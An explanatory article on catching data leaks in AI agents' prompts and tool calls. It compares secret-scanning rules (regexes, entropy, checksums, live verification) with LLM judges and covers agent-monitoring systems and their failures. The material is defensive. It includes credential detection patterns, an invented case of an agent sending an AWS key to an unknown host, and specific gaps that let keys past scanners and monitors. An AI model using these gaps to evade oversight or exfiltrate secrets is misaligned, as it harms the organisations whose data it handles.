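# Pattern detectors and LLM judges for catching data leaks in AI agent prompts and tool calls

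## What counts as a data leak when an agent acts

Leak detection for AI agents means inspecting what an agent reads, writes and sends so that an organisation's data does not reach people or systems that should not have it. It uses two kinds of check. Pattern detectors match the form of a string, such as the fixed prefix of an access key or the digits of a payment card. LLM judges are language models that check whether a message breaks a rule written in plain language, such as a ban on sending company data outside the company.

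Companies used data leak prevention (DLP) software long before they had agents. It monitors email, laptops and cloud storage and raises an alert when sensitive data leaves, often too late to stop it. IT Brew's *Is data leak prevention built for AI?* cites a survey of more than 433 IT professionals, run by the Cloud Security Alliance with a DLP vendor, in which the software blocked only 16% of reported detections before the data left. Agents make leaks harder to catch because moving data is a large part of their work. A travel assistant, for example, has to give the airline a passport number. Scoring a check on this traffic requires first deciding which transfers count as leaks, and that depends on more than the data itself.

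### Agents and tool calls

*The Claws in Plain Sight* (Dong, Lu and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent as a language model running in a loop. At each step, the model receives a task, descriptions of the available tools and the results of its earlier actions. It then writes either ordinary text or a tool call, which is a structured request containing a function's name and the arguments to run it with. The tool is conventional software that searches a mailbox, queries a database or runs a shell command. Software around the model executes the call and feeds the result back.

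Suppose an employee asks an agent to summarise a contract and email the summary to a supplier. The agent calls a file tool with the contract's location as the argument. The tool returns the full contract to the model's context, which is the text the model works from. The agent then calls an email tool with the supplier's address and the summary as arguments.

The model can draw those arguments from anything in its context, including the confidential clauses it was supposed to leave out. Dong and colleagues point out that ordinary tool permissions don't prevent this, because they control whether the agent may use the email tool but not which information it has read may go into a particular email.

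### The four inspection points

Gowda's *How we approach AI security*, the software vendor Speakeasy's account of its own design, lists four places to look for a leak in one pass through this loop: the user prompt, the tool call, the tool response and the model response.

People sometimes type or paste information into prompts that they should not share. In a survey of 5,000 adults reported by IT Brew, 32% of those who use AI at work said they had shared sensitive information with an AI tool without their employer knowing. Whether that is a leak depends on where the organisation allows its data to go. Pasting a customer list into a chatbot covered by a company contract may be fine, but pasting it into a personal account on an unapproved service probably is not.

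A tool call can send data anywhere the agent's tools reach, for example in the body of an email, a file upload, or a web request inside a shell command. Gowda thinks a policy can have the most effect at the tool call, because the action has not happened yet and the check can target one function or one pattern within the arguments.

A tool response carries data the other way, into the agent's context. A database query may return whole customer records when the agent needed one field. No data has gone to a third party at this stage, unless the model runs on an outside provider's servers and the organisation counts that provider as a third party. But the agent can include any record in its context in the arguments of a later tool call, so an alert at this stage can come before the data leaks.

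The model response is the text that the agent shows its user. It leaks data when it contains information the user is not entitled to see, as when a customer-service agent tells one customer what another has ordered.

Checks that read only the model's response can miss leaks in tool calls. An agent can send protected values in a tool call and then accurately report that the task is done, and many interfaces hide the raw arguments from the user. *When Agents Talk, Secrets Travel* (Ogundoyin and Ikram, 2026) cites an earlier benchmark of two cooperating agents in which audits of the final output alone missed 41.7% of violations. The paper's own seven-channel scheme covers tool arguments, tool results and final output, and adds messages between agents, shared memory, visible reasoning and logs, and the files that a system produces. The four points are enough to describe most traffic for a single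 agent, but the extra channels matter once agents delegate to one another.

### Sensitivity and permission

Whether a string is sensitive is a separate question from whether a particular recipient may have it for a particular purpose, but people who talk about leaks tend to confuse the two. A courier needs a home address, for example, while a product-support request usually does not. Dong and colleagues give the example of a company that might use a user's occupation to route a support query but forbid sending the same string to a marketing service.

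Redacting sensitive data without checking who will receive it can block disclosures that are allowed. Ogundoyin and Ikram ran 485 multi-agent scenarios, each with a written policy on who could receive what. Blanket redaction, which removes every detected value regardless of recipient, let through only 20.5% of the disclosures that the policies allowed. A filter that used the same detection but also checked the recipient let through 94.1% of them, with almost the same rate of unauthorised disclosure (29.25%, against 28.3% for blanket redaction).

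### Contextual integrity

The usual account of permission comes from privacy theory. In *Privacy as Contextual Integrity*, Nissenbaum (2004) wanted to explain what is wrong with public surveillance, such as the use of cameras and shopper cards to gather facts that people have not exactly hidden. She proposed that privacy depends on the norms of a particular setting, which govern both what is appropriate to reveal there and where the information may travel afterwards. Zimmer (2005), in *Privacy as Contextual Integrity (Part 2)*, quotes her definition of the norms of appropriateness, which cover what is "allowable, expected, or even demanded to be revealed". He gives the example of a medical visit, where it is appropriate to discuss a patient's physical condition but not their salary.

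Most work on agents uses the five-part version of contextual integrity in *Contextual Integrity Up and Down the Data Food Chain* (Nissenbaum, 2019). A full description of an information flow includes the sender, the recipient, the subject (the person the information is about), the type of information and the transmission principle. The transmission principle is the condition under which the information moves, such as with the subject's consent, in confidence, by legal requirement or for sale. A doctor who passes a patient's blood results to a specialist in confidence satisfies the norms of medicine. Passing the same results to the patient's employer would violate those norms, even though the results are no more sensitive.

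The theory has no presumption against sharing, and a flow that fits the norms is no loss of privacy. It also requires all five values to be specified. Nissenbaum reports survey experiments in which people interpreted descriptions differently when some values were left out. A company rule such as "do not share confidential data" is ambiguous in the same way because it omits the recipient and the condition. She allows shortcuts in narrow settings where one value hardly varies, so a check on a company's own agents can reasonably treat the sender as fixed.

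*PrivacyFlow* (2026) describes contextual integrity as the de facto standard for reasoning about such expectations, but the theory fits company data imperfectly. Nissenbaum's theory concerns personal information, and a merger plan or a source file has no data subject in her sense. *CI-Work* (Fu, Qin and colleagues, 2026) applies the theory to business tasks by sorting everything an agent retrieves into entries the recipient needs and entries the recipient should not get. In one of its examples of a failure, an agent reveals the walk-away price during a negotiation, which damages the company but discloses no personal information.

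Purpose also fits the framework only loosely. It is not one of the five parameters, although a transmission principle can partly express it. Nissenbaum writes that her collaborator Anupam Datta urged her to add a parameter for use, and that she is increasingly persuaded. Agents strengthen the case for adding one because they often hold data for one task and use it in another.

*Say Something Else* (2026) cites research showing that people often disagree about what violates the norms, depending on their experience and preferences. When Fu and colleagues had human annotators check their labels, agreement ranged from 82.5% to 95.0%, even though the cases were built to be clear. Some of what a test counts as a check's errors will therefore be disagreements about the policy.

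### Four example calls

The following four invented calls involve an agent at a company that uses Amazon Web Services (AWS) and is planning to buy a competitor. AWS access keys are credentials with a recognisable form.

1. The agent posts an AWS key to an unknown outside host.
2. The agent sends the same key to the company's own secrets manager, a protected store for credentials.
3. The agent uploads the unannounced acquisition plans to a public file-sharing site.
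4. The agent sends the same plans to the outside law firm that the user named in the request.

| Invented example calls | Leak | Not a leak |
|---|---|---|
| **Recognisable pattern** | Call 1: AWS key to an unknown outside host | Call 2: AWS key to the company's secrets manager |
| **No recognisable pattern** | Call 3: acquisition plans to a public file-sharing site | Call 4: acquisition plans to the law firm the user named |

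A pattern detector with no other information flags both calls in the top row and passes both in the bottom row. It catches the stolen key, raises a false alarm over routine storage and misses the exposed plans. It correctly passes the email to the lawyers, but only because the plans contain nothing for it to match.

The columns differ in who receives the data and on what terms. The law treats acquisition plans in much the same way. Under Article 10 of the Market Abuse Regulation, *Unlawful disclosure of inside information*, passing on inside information is unlawful except "in the normal exercise of an employment, a profession or duties". The US Securities and Exchange Commission's selective-disclosure rule (2021) exempts disclosure to someone who owes the company a duty of trust or confidence, and its first example is an attorney.

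Call 3 is a contextual leak, a transfer that is wrong because of who receives the data or why, whatever the data looks like. Some evidence suggests that agents are especially prone to these leaks. In *AgentCIScope*, Guo, Chen and colleagues (2026) tested 12 agents on 936 office tasks and found average leakage rates of 17.1% for credit-card information and 29.4% for US Social Security numbers, compared with 76.5% for booking details and 84.7% for personal preferences. They wrote the task instructions to tempt agents into oversharing, so these rates are a poor guide to how often agents leak data in ordinary use. The difference between data types is more informative. The agents already guarded card numbers, which a pattern can catch, far better than information with no fixed form.

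Contextual leaks also happen inside a company. In one case that Guo and colleagues describe, an HR employee asks an agent to send a hiring manager an update on a candidate, and the agent includes the candidate's background check. A ban on external data transfer would not block that message if the manager works for the same company. Fu and colleagues found that the models they tested generally leaked less to external parties than to colleagues. GPT-5, for instance, disclosed about 4% of the sensitive entries in external exchanges and 18% in exchanges between peers. A rule against external transfer is easier to write, but another control is needed to catch internal leaks.

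### Recall, precision and false positive rate

A check can err by passing a leak or by flagging a harmless message, and three ratios describe how often these errors happen. The counts below come from the rates that Ogundoyin and Ikram published for a judge model on 299 passages labelled by two experts. Here a "leak" is a passage that disclosed a particular protected value, in the original words or in paraphrase. The researchers handled the recipient's permission separately.

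| | Leak | Harmless | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| **Flagged** | 30 | 3 | 33 |
| **Passed** | 2 | 264 | 266 |
| **Total** | 32 | 267 | 299 |

Recall is the share of real leaks that the check flags, which is 30 of 32, or 94%. The two leaks it missed are false negatives. The false positive rate is the share of harmless messages that it flags, which is 3 of 267, or 1.1%. Precision is the share of flagged messages that are real leaks, which is 30 of 33, or 91%.

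These numbers are optimistic because the researchers chose the judge's cut-off score for flagging using the same 299 passages. Raising the cut-off from 0.5 to above 0.9 reduces false alarms from three to one, but the judge then catches only 20 of the 32 leaks.

Precision depends on how common leaks are, and in this sample about one passage in nine was a leak. If a company's agents sent 100,000 messages, of which 100 were leaks, and recall and the false positive rate stayed the same, the judge would catch about 94 leaks and raise about 1,120 false alarms. Precision would drop to roughly 8%, and a reviewer would open about a dozen harmless messages for each real leak.

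### What each kind of check costs

Pattern detectors check only whether data is sensitive, and only for data with a known form. They always give the same verdict for the same input and, according to Gowda, add almost no delay. LLM judges try to determine whether sharing the data is permitted. Each check requires a model call, and the agent must wait for the verdict before acting, so the judge delays every step it covers. It can also give different verdicts on identical runs. Gowda writes as a vendor and gives no measurements, but the direction of the trade-off follows from how the two techniques work.

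A judge can only try to decide whether sharing data is permitted from the information it has, and a tool call often leaves out what it needs. In the traces that Ogundoyin and Ikram examined, messages between agents and reads from shared memory identified an addressee, but tool arguments did not. A web address in an argument gives a destination but doesn't show who controls it. In the acquisition plans example, call 4 is acceptable because the user named the law firm in the prompt. A judge that sees only the tool call sees a confidential document and an outside email address, and would have good reason to flag it.

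## How pattern detectors find secrets and identifiers

Companies usually switch on a detector catalogue, a maintained collection of rules grouped by type of data, rather than writing each pattern detector themselves. For example, the catalogue in Speakeasy's *Guardrails* documentation has categories for secrets, financial information, personal information, government identifiers and healthcare records.

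A rule can check a string's form, the words near it, how random it looks, whether its checksum is valid, and whether it works when used. Most rules apply only some of these five tests. For example, all five can apply to a GitHub personal access token, a credential that lets software act on a user's GitHub account.

### Form and nearby keywords

Gitleaks, an open-source secret scanner, finds this token with a regular expression, which is a compact description of a set of strings:

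`ghp_[0-9a-zA-Z]{36}`

The rule's regular expression matches `ghp_` followed by 36 digits or letters. The rule also lists `ghp_` as a keyword. Gitleaks searches for a rule's keywords first and runs the expression only if it finds one, so a message without the prefix takes very little time to check.

Keywords matter more when a secret has no prefix. A generic API-key rule in the Gitleaks test data looks for a word such as "key", "token" or "password", then an assignment sign shortly after it, then a value of 10 to 150 characters. Such a rule can catch formats that have no specific rule, but it can also match ordinary text. *A Comparative Study of Software Secrets Reporting by Secret Detection Tools* (Basak, Cox and colleagues, 2023) gives an example from TruffleHog, another open-source scanner. TruffleHog's rule for GitLab tokens accepted any run of 20 to 22 suitable characters near the word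 "gitlab", so it reported `add-a-file-using-the-`, part of a web address in GitLab's documentation, as a token.

Regular expressions can also fail because of the characters next to a secret. In *Boundary-Mutation Testing for Pattern-Based Secret Detection*, Mishra (2026) placed fake credentials in 12 contexts, such as a quoted assignment, a web address and a function argument. Gitleaks 8.21.2 caught an AWS access key inside quotation marks but missed one written as an unquoted function argument. Its rule accepted a key only if the next character was on a short list, which included quotation marks, spaces and semicolons but not commas, closing brackets or ampersands. The rules for six of the nine credential types that Gitleaks detected had this fault.

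Web addresses use ampersands to separate parameters, so a key in the middle of an address often has an ampersand after it. If an agent sends a key this way in a shell command, even a rule written for that kind of key could miss it.

### Randomness

Services usually generate credentials at random, so many rules also test how random a string looks. The usual measure is Shannon entropy:

H = −Σ p log₂ p

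For each distinct character, p is its share of the string. The result is in bits per character. A string of one repeated letter scores 0, and a string that uses 16 different characters equally often scores 4. The generic Gitleaks rule requires at least 3.5.

Many harmless strings pass this test. A commit hash, the ID that the version-control system Git gives each saved change, is typically 40 hexadecimal digits long. Hexadecimal has 16 symbols, and the hash function spreads them fairly evenly, so the score is usually close to the maximum of 4. UUIDs, the 32-digit hexadecimal IDs that software assigns to records, score high for the same reason. Both kinds of ID look random because they have to be unique, and neither normally grants access to anything.

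A sample report in the Gitleaks documentation lists a made-up credential, `cafebabe:deadbeef`, with an entropy of 2.61. The hash of the commit that contained it scores 3.53 by the same formula, so a threshold of 3.5 would discard the credential and keep the hash.

Ordinary words can also have high entropy, because entropy measures how evenly a string uses its characters and a short phrase may repeat few letters. Basak and colleagues compare the dummy value `ThisIsAReallyLongString`, which scores 4.09, with a random-looking string of 47 characters, which scores 4.12.

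### Checksums

GitHub's old tokens were 40 hexadecimal characters long, so they looked the same as commit hashes. In 2021 GitHub introduced the `ghp_` prefix to make tokens easier to find. It expected the prefix alone to cut the false positive rate of its secret scanning to 0.5%, but its announcement included no measurement.

The new tokens also contain a checksum, a short value calculated from the rest of the string. The 30 characters after the prefix are random, and the last six encode a CRC32 checksum. A detector can recalculate it without contacting GitHub. The open-source keyhog-scanner removes the prefix, computes the checksum of the 30 random characters and compares it with the last six. A random string of the right form would pass about once in 57 billion attempts. GitHub's *announcing npms new access token format* describes the same design for npm, a registry of JavaScript packages.

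Payment cards use a much weaker checksum, the Luhn algorithm. Starting from the right, the detector doubles every second digit and subtracts 9 from any result above 9. It then adds up all the digits, and the number passes if the total is a multiple of 10. For 4111 1111 1111 1111:

- the 4 becomes 8
- seven of the 1s become 2s, which adds 14
- the other eight 1s stay as they are, which adds 8

The total is 30, so the number passes. But it is a published test number that developers use to try out payment forms, and no customer's card has it.

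One in ten random digit strings also passes the check, because exactly one choice of final digit makes the total a multiple of 10. The check is meant to catch typing errors, and it does that well. When used to detect leaks, it rules out about 90% of random 16-digit numbers, but the rest still look like card numbers. A company that generates a million 16-digit order numbers can expect about 100,000 to pass, though a rule that also checks the opening digits will reject some of them.

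A checksum can confirm a string's form but can't show that the string is sensitive. Even GitHub's stronger checksum has this limit. Its formula is public, so anyone can write an example token that passes, and a revoked token still passes. Babyak describes the same problem with identifiers in a Speakeasy product post, *Tune risk detection sensitivity, one policy at a time*. A rule for personal data may flag an internal ID that looks like an international bank account number.

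### Live verification

Using a credential is the most direct way to find out whether it works. A scanner with live verification sends the possible credential to the service that would have issued it, usually in a harmless request such as asking which account it belongs to. If the service accepts the credential, the scanner can report a working secret with very little doubt.

A rejection is harder to interpret because the string may never have been a credential, its owner may have revoked it, or it may work only inside a private network. The scanner can't verify some secrets, such as a private key with no known server, because it has no service to test them against. Verification also needs network access, and Mishra had to switch off TruffleHog's live checks because the test environment had none. In a system that inspects each tool call before it runs, the agent would have to wait for an outside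 service to respond.

Checking whether a detected key works improves precision by removing test values and expired keys, but it doesn't show whether the transfer is allowed. For example, an alert about a working key being sent to the company's own secrets manager is a false alarm.

### Matching a company's own data

Many of the values a company wants to protect have no public format. Exact data matching finds them by comparing traffic with the company's own records. The company exports selected columns from a database, such as customer numbers and surnames, and software converts each value into a hash, a fixed-length code that is always the same for the same input. The detector hashes the words and numbers in a message the same way and looks for matches. A rule often requires two values from the same row, because a surname alone would match far too much text.

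This approach can tell a real customer number from a random string of the same length, which a regular expression can't do. The index needs regular updates, and the detector has to allow for differences in spacing and punctuation. The company also has to guard the index, because hashing only weakly protects short identifiers. There are only a billion possible nine-digit numbers, so someone who stole the index and knew how the company made the hashes could try them all.

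Document fingerprinting detects text copied from confidential documents. The software splits each document into overlapping runs of words, hashes them and stores some of the hashes. It flags an outgoing message that contains enough of the same runs, even if the sender copied only a few paragraphs. A summary in new words will probably pass because it shares few runs with the original. This weakness matters more for agents than for people copying files, because agents often summarise documents.

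Names and places are hard for all of these methods to detect. Microsoft Presidio, an open-source tool for finding personal data, combines pattern rules with named-entity recognition, in which a trained model labels parts of a text as people, places or organisations. Presidio gives each match a confidence score. A loose digit pattern starts with a low score, and a passed checksum or a nearby word such as "card" raises it. The operator sets a threshold and ignores matches below it.

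No single threshold is correct for every scan. Babyak reports that Speakeasy uses a default of 0.5, and that raising it to 0.75 on a sample of 100,000 production messages began to drop real findings. Babyak doesn't say how many, so the tradeoff is hard to judge, but suggests setting the threshold separately for each policy. False alarms are more tolerable when scanning user prompts for secrets than when scanning a database tool that returns customer records all day.

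### Exclusion lists

Some false alarms recur daily because the same harmless values keep appearing in documentation and tests. An exclusion list, or allowlist, tells the detector to ignore these values. GitLab's list for Gitleaks includes an example token from its documentation whose body is `1234567890abcdefghij`. Speakeasy's *Exclusion Rules* documentation describes a built-in, read-only library of published test card numbers and example keys. Customers write separate rules for their own harmless values.

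The sample configuration in the Gitleaks documentation excludes 078-05-1120, a US Social Security number that became famous in the 1930s after a wallet manufacturer printed it on sample cards. It also excludes numbers that start with 9 or 666, which the Social Security Administration doesn't issue.

Excluding one exact value is fairly safe, but broader exclusions can hide real leaks. Gitleaks can skip whole files or any secret that contains a chosen word, so it would miss a real key in a skipped test file. Speakeasy lets an administrator exclude a single value under a single rule or silence every finding from a rule.

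These exclusions also filter by what the detector matched, regardless of the recipient. In the earlier example, an agent posts an AWS key to an unknown host in call 1 and stores the same key in the company's secrets manager in call 2. If the company excludes that key to stop alerts about call 2, it also silences the alert for call 1.

### Measured precision and recall

Researchers have mostly tested secret scanners on source code, so their figures are only a rough guide to recall on agent traffic. In 2023, Basak and colleagues ran the largest comparison described here, testing nine tools on SecretBench, a collection of 818 public repositories with 97,479 hand-labelled candidate strings. Of these, 15,084 were real secrets, 4,457 of them unique.

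| Tool | Alerts | Correct alerts | Precision | Unique secrets found | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GitHub secret scanner | 1,721 | 1,292 | 75% | 1,606 | 36% |
| Gitleaks | 45,932 | 21,047 | 46% | 3,901 | 88% |
| TruffleHog | 90,982 | 5,426 | 6% | 2,323 | 52% |
| SpectralOps | 1,547,994 | 4,777 | under 1% | 2,979 | 67% |

Recall here is the share of secrets that a tool reported at least once, anywhere in the repository. No tool did well on both precision and recall. GitHub's scanner raised few false alarms but missed nearly two-thirds of the secrets. SpectralOps, a commercial scanner, found two-thirds of them but produced about 1.5 million alerts.

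Results also depended heavily on the type of secret. Gitleaks found 99% of private keys but only 41% of database and server addresses containing credentials, while TruffleHog found 59% of the keys and 98% of the addresses. When Basak and colleagues examined samples of missed secrets, they found faulty regular expressions, file types that a tool skipped, and services for which it had no rule.

The recall figures are probably too high for secrets in general. SecretBench contains only candidates that matched at least one of 761 regular expressions, so it leaves out any secret that matched none of them. The study also tested versions of the tools that are now several years old.

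Newer work suggests false alarms are still common. In *Argus*, Wang, Li and colleagues (2026) scanned public repositories with TruffleHog and had two security specialists label 2,000 of its findings, with a third settling disagreements. Fewer than 3.4% were genuine leaks. Rules for GitHub and GitLab tokens produced 72.4% of all findings, and many of those were commit hashes or default configuration files.

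Argus uses language models to check TruffleHog's findings. It first examines the string for placeholders or an invalid format. It can then read the surrounding text for signs that the value is an example, and search the project for files that use it. In one case, Argus judged a private key genuine because the project's payment code loaded it.

The researchers compared Argus with other tools on 97 candidates from TruffleHog's output. They list 57 of these as real leaks, but their recall percentages match a total of 56. Argus had a precision of 96.36% and a recall of 94.64%, compared with 78.79% and 46.43% for Gitleaks. These percentages correspond to 53 real leaks and two false alarms for Argus, and 26 real leaks and seven false alarms for Gitleaks. A single prompt to GPT-4o, the model Argus uses, had a precision of 72.22% and a recall of 92.86%.

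Argus has much higher recall than Gitleaks, but the precision figures depend on only a few errors. Every candidate came from TruffleHog, so the test excludes secrets that TruffleHog missed, and Argus cannot recover them. Argus took about 42 seconds per candidate, which is fine for an overnight scan but slow for a check that must finish before an agent's tool call can run.

Other scanners use a machine-learning model trained on labelled secrets, and their published scores also need some caution. *From Data Leak to Secret Misses* (2026) found that duplicated samples can inflate results by up to 26% on a standard measure of classification quality, and it calls for these models to be re-evaluated.

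Mishra published the most recent comparison in September 2026 and declined to rank the tools. It tested Gitleaks, TruffleHog and Mishra's own scanner on 400 generated credentials of ten types and 700 harmless lines. Gitleaks found 80% or 90% of the credentials, depending on how realistic they were, and TruffleHog found 60%. Mishra's scanner found all the credentials but raised 17 false alarms on the harmless lines, while the other two raised none.

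Each tool found either all 40 credentials of a given type or none of them. The test therefore amounts to ten observations per tool instead of 400, and none of the differences in recall was statistically significant. For a company choosing a scanner, testing each type of credential it uses is more useful than comparing average recall.

The way a test presents a credential can also change the result. TruffleHog found none of the AWS access key IDs when they appeared alone, but all of them when the matching secret key was in the same file. On 292,527 lines of code from four real projects, Mishra's scanner had the fewest false alarms per line, though it had ranked worst for false alarms on the artificial examples. Many of the other tools' false alarms came from one of the four projects, the scanner's own repository, which contains imitation credentials. In the three outside projects, Mishra's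 scanner raised 10 false alarms, Gitleaks 12 and TruffleHog 27.

### The four example calls

A catalogue with a working AWS rule flags calls 1 and 2, which carry the key, and lets through calls 3 and 4, which carry the acquisition plans. Even the alert for call 1 depends on details such as which character follows the key and whether the tool also requires the matching secret key to be present.

Better rules would largely solve the problem of unrecognised formats. Developers can add missing rules or repair faulty ones, and issuers can make their tokens easier to find, as GitHub did. Mishra found five rules in their own scanner that missed some or all credentials ending in a hyphen. For SendGrid, an email service, this meant missing about one key in 64. A small change fixed all five rules without adding false alarms on real code. An earlier fix had looked just as reasonable but made two of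 the rules miss keys they used to catch, so repaired rules need testing too.

Better rules can also recover some hidden values. Encoding can hide a secret by changing its form, even when nobody intends to evade the detector. Email software, for example, routinely encodes attachments. Gitleaks can decode three common encodings before it searches, although version 8.26.0 leaves this off by default. A detector that examines one message at a time will still miss a secret split between two messages if neither contains a complete match.

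These techniques don't help when the data has no distinctive format. For example, you can't write a regular expression for news of an unannounced acquisition. A keyword rule for the deal's code name would catch some messages about it, and a document fingerprint would catch copied passages. Both would block the upload to the public site in call 3, but also the email to the law firm in call 4.

Better rules can't separate calls 1 and 2 either, because both contain the same key. Telling them apart requires information about the recipient, such as a list of approved destinations or a policy that a judge can apply.

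## How an LLM judge applies a plain-language policy

An LLM judge can try to tell calls 1 and 2 apart by comparing the recipient with a written rule. *Custom guardrail examples*, from the product documentation of the data company Databricks, recommends an exact rule when something like a tool name or an argument value settles the question, and a judge when the check depends on meaning. With a judge, most of the difficulty is in writing the policy and giving the judge enough information to apply it.

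### One evaluation from start to finish

Speakeasy, a vendor, describes its prompt-based policies in its own documentation, which gives no accuracy figures. An administrator describes the behaviour to flag or edits one of three templates, such as "External data transfer". The administrator also sets the scope and the judge's temperature, which controls how random its word choices are. In August 2026 Speakeasy listed Gemini 3.1 Flash Lite, a lightweight Google model, as the default judge, with Claude Sonnet 4.6 and Claude Haiku 4.5 as alternatives.

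Suppose the agent attempts call 1, a shell command that posts the AWS key to an outside host. Speakeasy first checks the command against the scope and sends it to the judge only if the scope covers shell tool calls.

The judge is an ordinary language model whose only information about the company's private arrangements comes from its prompt. That prompt has to include the policy, the message and instructions on how to answer. Fu and colleagues published a prompt of this kind, which they used to check the test data for CI-Work, their benchmark for enterprise agents. The model receives the sender, the recipient and the task, and must classify each item of information as essential, sensitive or ambiguous, writing a reason before each label. Because a language model writes its answer from left to right, the reason can influence the label only if it comes first.

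Software then has to read the answer, which is less trivial than it sounds. Ayyagari (2026), in *Pinned and Still Unstable*, let Gemini 2.5 Pro give its verdicts in free text and could not extract about 24% of them, because the model ran on until it hit the length limit. Ayyagari blames this partly on an unusually small reasoning budget. Forcing the answer into a fixed structure removed nearly all the failures. For call 1, a structured answer might look like this invented one:

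`{"reason": "The command posts an AWS key to a host outside the company.", "flag": true, "confidence": 0.95}`

Speakeasy's judge returns a yes-or-no verdict, a confidence score and a written rationale, which reviewers see beside the finding. The judge in Bifrost's *Prompt Guardrails* returns `ALLOW` or `BLOCK`, with a reason if it blocks. *Protect agentic AI applications with Datadog AI Guard*, by Bordeau, Mola and George, describes tags such as `data-exfiltration`, each with a probability.

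The written reason helps a reviewer find the judge's mistakes quickly, such as misreading a company address as an outside one. But the model generates the reason the same way it generates the verdict, and a fluent explanation is no evidence that the verdict is right.

### A vague policy and a precise one

Speakeasy doesn't publish the wording of its external-transfer template, so both of the following policies are invented. The vague one has four words:

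> Flag external data transfer.

The precise one defines the boundary, the data and the exceptions:

> Flag any tool call that sends company data to a recipient outside the company. Company data means credentials, customer records, source code, and business, legal or financial plans that the company has not published. Inside the company means example.com addresses and AWS account 111122223333. Treat a recipient you cannot identify as outside. Do not flag documents sent to Marlow & Pike (marlowpike.example), the company's law firm, if the user asked to send them there, unless they contain credentials.

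The table applies each policy to the four example calls. The verdicts follow from the wording and are not the output of a model.

| Call | Vague policy | Precise policy | What the call may not show |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1: AWS key to an unknown outside host | Flag | Flag | Who controls the host |
| 2: AWS key to the company's secrets manager | Could go either way | Pass, if the judge can see the account | Which AWS account receives the key |
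| 3: Acquisition plans to a public file-sharing site | Probably flag | Flag, if the judge can see the contents | What the file contains, and whether the company has published it |
| 4: Acquisition plans to the law firm | Probably flag | Pass, if the judge can see the request | That the user asked for the transfer |

Call 2 shows why "external" needs a definition. If the company uses Amazon's hosted secrets manager, the key goes to a server that Amazon runs, but into an account that the company controls. The precise policy settles whether this is external by naming the company's account. But all Amazon's customers in a region normally use the same web address for the service, so the call may not show whose account it is. The judge would then have to flag a harmless transfer, because the policy tells it to flag unidentified recipients. Reversing that instruction would remove this false alarm,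 but the judge would then have no reason to flag the unknown host in call 1.

Call 3 may not include the data being sent. An upload command often contains only a file's location, such as `/deals/heron-final.pdf`, so a judge that sees only the command has to guess the contents from the name.

The precise policy requires both a named firm and a request from the user in call 4. A request alone isn't enough, because employees can also ask an agent to send customer records to their personal email. If a named firm were enough, the agent could send that firm any company document without being asked.

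A complete definition of what each recipient may receive quickly becomes long. In Guo and colleagues' benchmark, the rule for each task lists every protected value, the person it concerns, its type and the outsiders who must not receive it. This level of detail is practical for an invented task but not for all of a company's traffic, so a real policy has to use categories and leave some interpretation to the judge.

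There is little evidence on how much precise wording helps. In *LLM-as-a-Judge for Privacy Evaluation?*, Meisenbacher, Klymenko and Matthes (2025) asked 13 models to rate the sensitivity of 250 texts from 1 to 5. One prompt described only the two ends of the scale, while the other defined all five ratings and asked for a reason. Agreement among the models rose from 0.54 to 0.58 on Krippendorff's alpha, where 1 is perfect agreement and 0 is what chance would produce. Part of this small gain may come from asking for reasons. The models could also agree with one another and all be wrong.

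### How much context to supply

A judge can receive a tool call alone, the call plus the user's request, or the whole session. Speakeasy's documentation describes a judge that evaluates each message in scope, but it doesn't specify how much of the earlier session the judge receives.

The judge can decide call 1 from the call alone, since no ordinary request would justify posting a live key to an unknown host. It can decide call 4 if it also sees the user's request. For call 3, it may need the earlier tool response in which the agent read the file, because the file's contents might appear nowhere else.

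Some leaks also build up over several calls, none of which breaks the policy by itself. Help Net Security's *Bedrock Data enhances AI agent governance with intent-aware DLP* gives one vendor's example of a name, a date of birth and a medical diagnosis accumulating over a session. The vendor's product checks each action against the user's inferred purpose and earlier actions, then reviews the whole session. Datadog's judge likewise reads the system prompt, the user's messages and previous actions before deciding on a tool call, according to Bordeau and colleagues. Neither account includes accuracy measurements.

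Checking each step against the full session takes more computation as the session grows. If each of 50 steps adds 1,000 tokens (the word fragments that models process), a judge that reads only the newest step processes 50,000 tokens in total. A judge that rereads the whole session at every step processes 1,000 × (1 + 2 + … + 50), or 1,275,000 tokens, about 25 times as many. Providers can reuse some of the computation for repeated text, but the judge still receives far more company data.

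A judge may need facts that the session history doesn't contain, such as who owns a domain or whether a supplier has signed a confidentiality agreement. One option is to let the judge report that a fact is missing and name it. *ContextLens* (2026) tested this for legal compliance, including cases under the EU's data protection law. Two graduate students with legal training checked samples of 30 cases and agreed with the models that a fact was missing, with agreement above 0.9 on a scale where 1 is perfect. But the three models often named different facts, and agreement among them was only 0.21 on the data protection cases. When drafting a policy, it would therefore make sense to ask more than one model which facts are missing from a borderline call.

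### Snowflake's two-stage detector

Snowflake, a cloud data company, has published one of the few results on the effect of added context in live agent traffic. Its Dangerous Agent Activity Detection examines trajectories, the full sequences of steps that agents take, for cyberattacks, help with biological weapons, and policy violations such as unauthorised disclosure. A lightweight model screens each trajectory, and a stronger reasoning model then assesses the suspicious ones with extra information, such as the user's role and permissions.

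Snowflake ran a three-week trial on about 6,000 sessions from staff who attack the company's systems to test security. The detector initially found potentially risky activity for every participating user, but it issued no alerts after taking into account what their testing covered.

The measured gain is therefore a drop from all users to none, and Snowflake does not report how precision or recall changed. The result is still useful because permission is often the only difference between security testing and a real attack. But a detector that ignored everything these testers did would have produced the same result. The second stage also uses a stronger model, so the extra context may not explain all of the improvement.

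In a separate trial on about 12,000 trajectories from ordinary engineering staff, the detector flagged three people. One case was a real incident in which an agent had terminated a process for all users of a cloud workspace. The other two involved development work that resembled a network scan. Three reasoning models also reviewed every trajectory, including those the detector had not flagged, and people examined the cases on which the models disagreed. Snowflake doesn't report how many missed cases this review found, so the detector's recall is unknown.

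Snowflake now runs the detector on about 18,000 internal trajectories a day and reports flagging fewer than 0.2% of them, or fewer than 36 a day. A security team could plausibly review that many, but the flag rate doesn't measure how many flags are correct.

### Verdicts that change between runs

An LLM judge can give different verdicts on an identical call, which matters for audits as well as for accuracy. Speakeasy argues against relying on an agent's own refusals, which it says leave "no record of what it would stop next time". The same objection applies to a judge whose verdicts vary.

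Lowering the temperature to 0, so that the model always picks its most likely next word, makes repeated verdicts differ less often but doesn't eliminate the differences. *The Coin Flip Judge?* (2026) measured how often they occurred. For GPT-4o-mini, the rate fell from 13.3% at temperature 1 to 2.8% at temperature 0. For GPT-4.1-mini, it fell only from 13.9% to 7.9%, and on one question it was still 50% at temperature 0.

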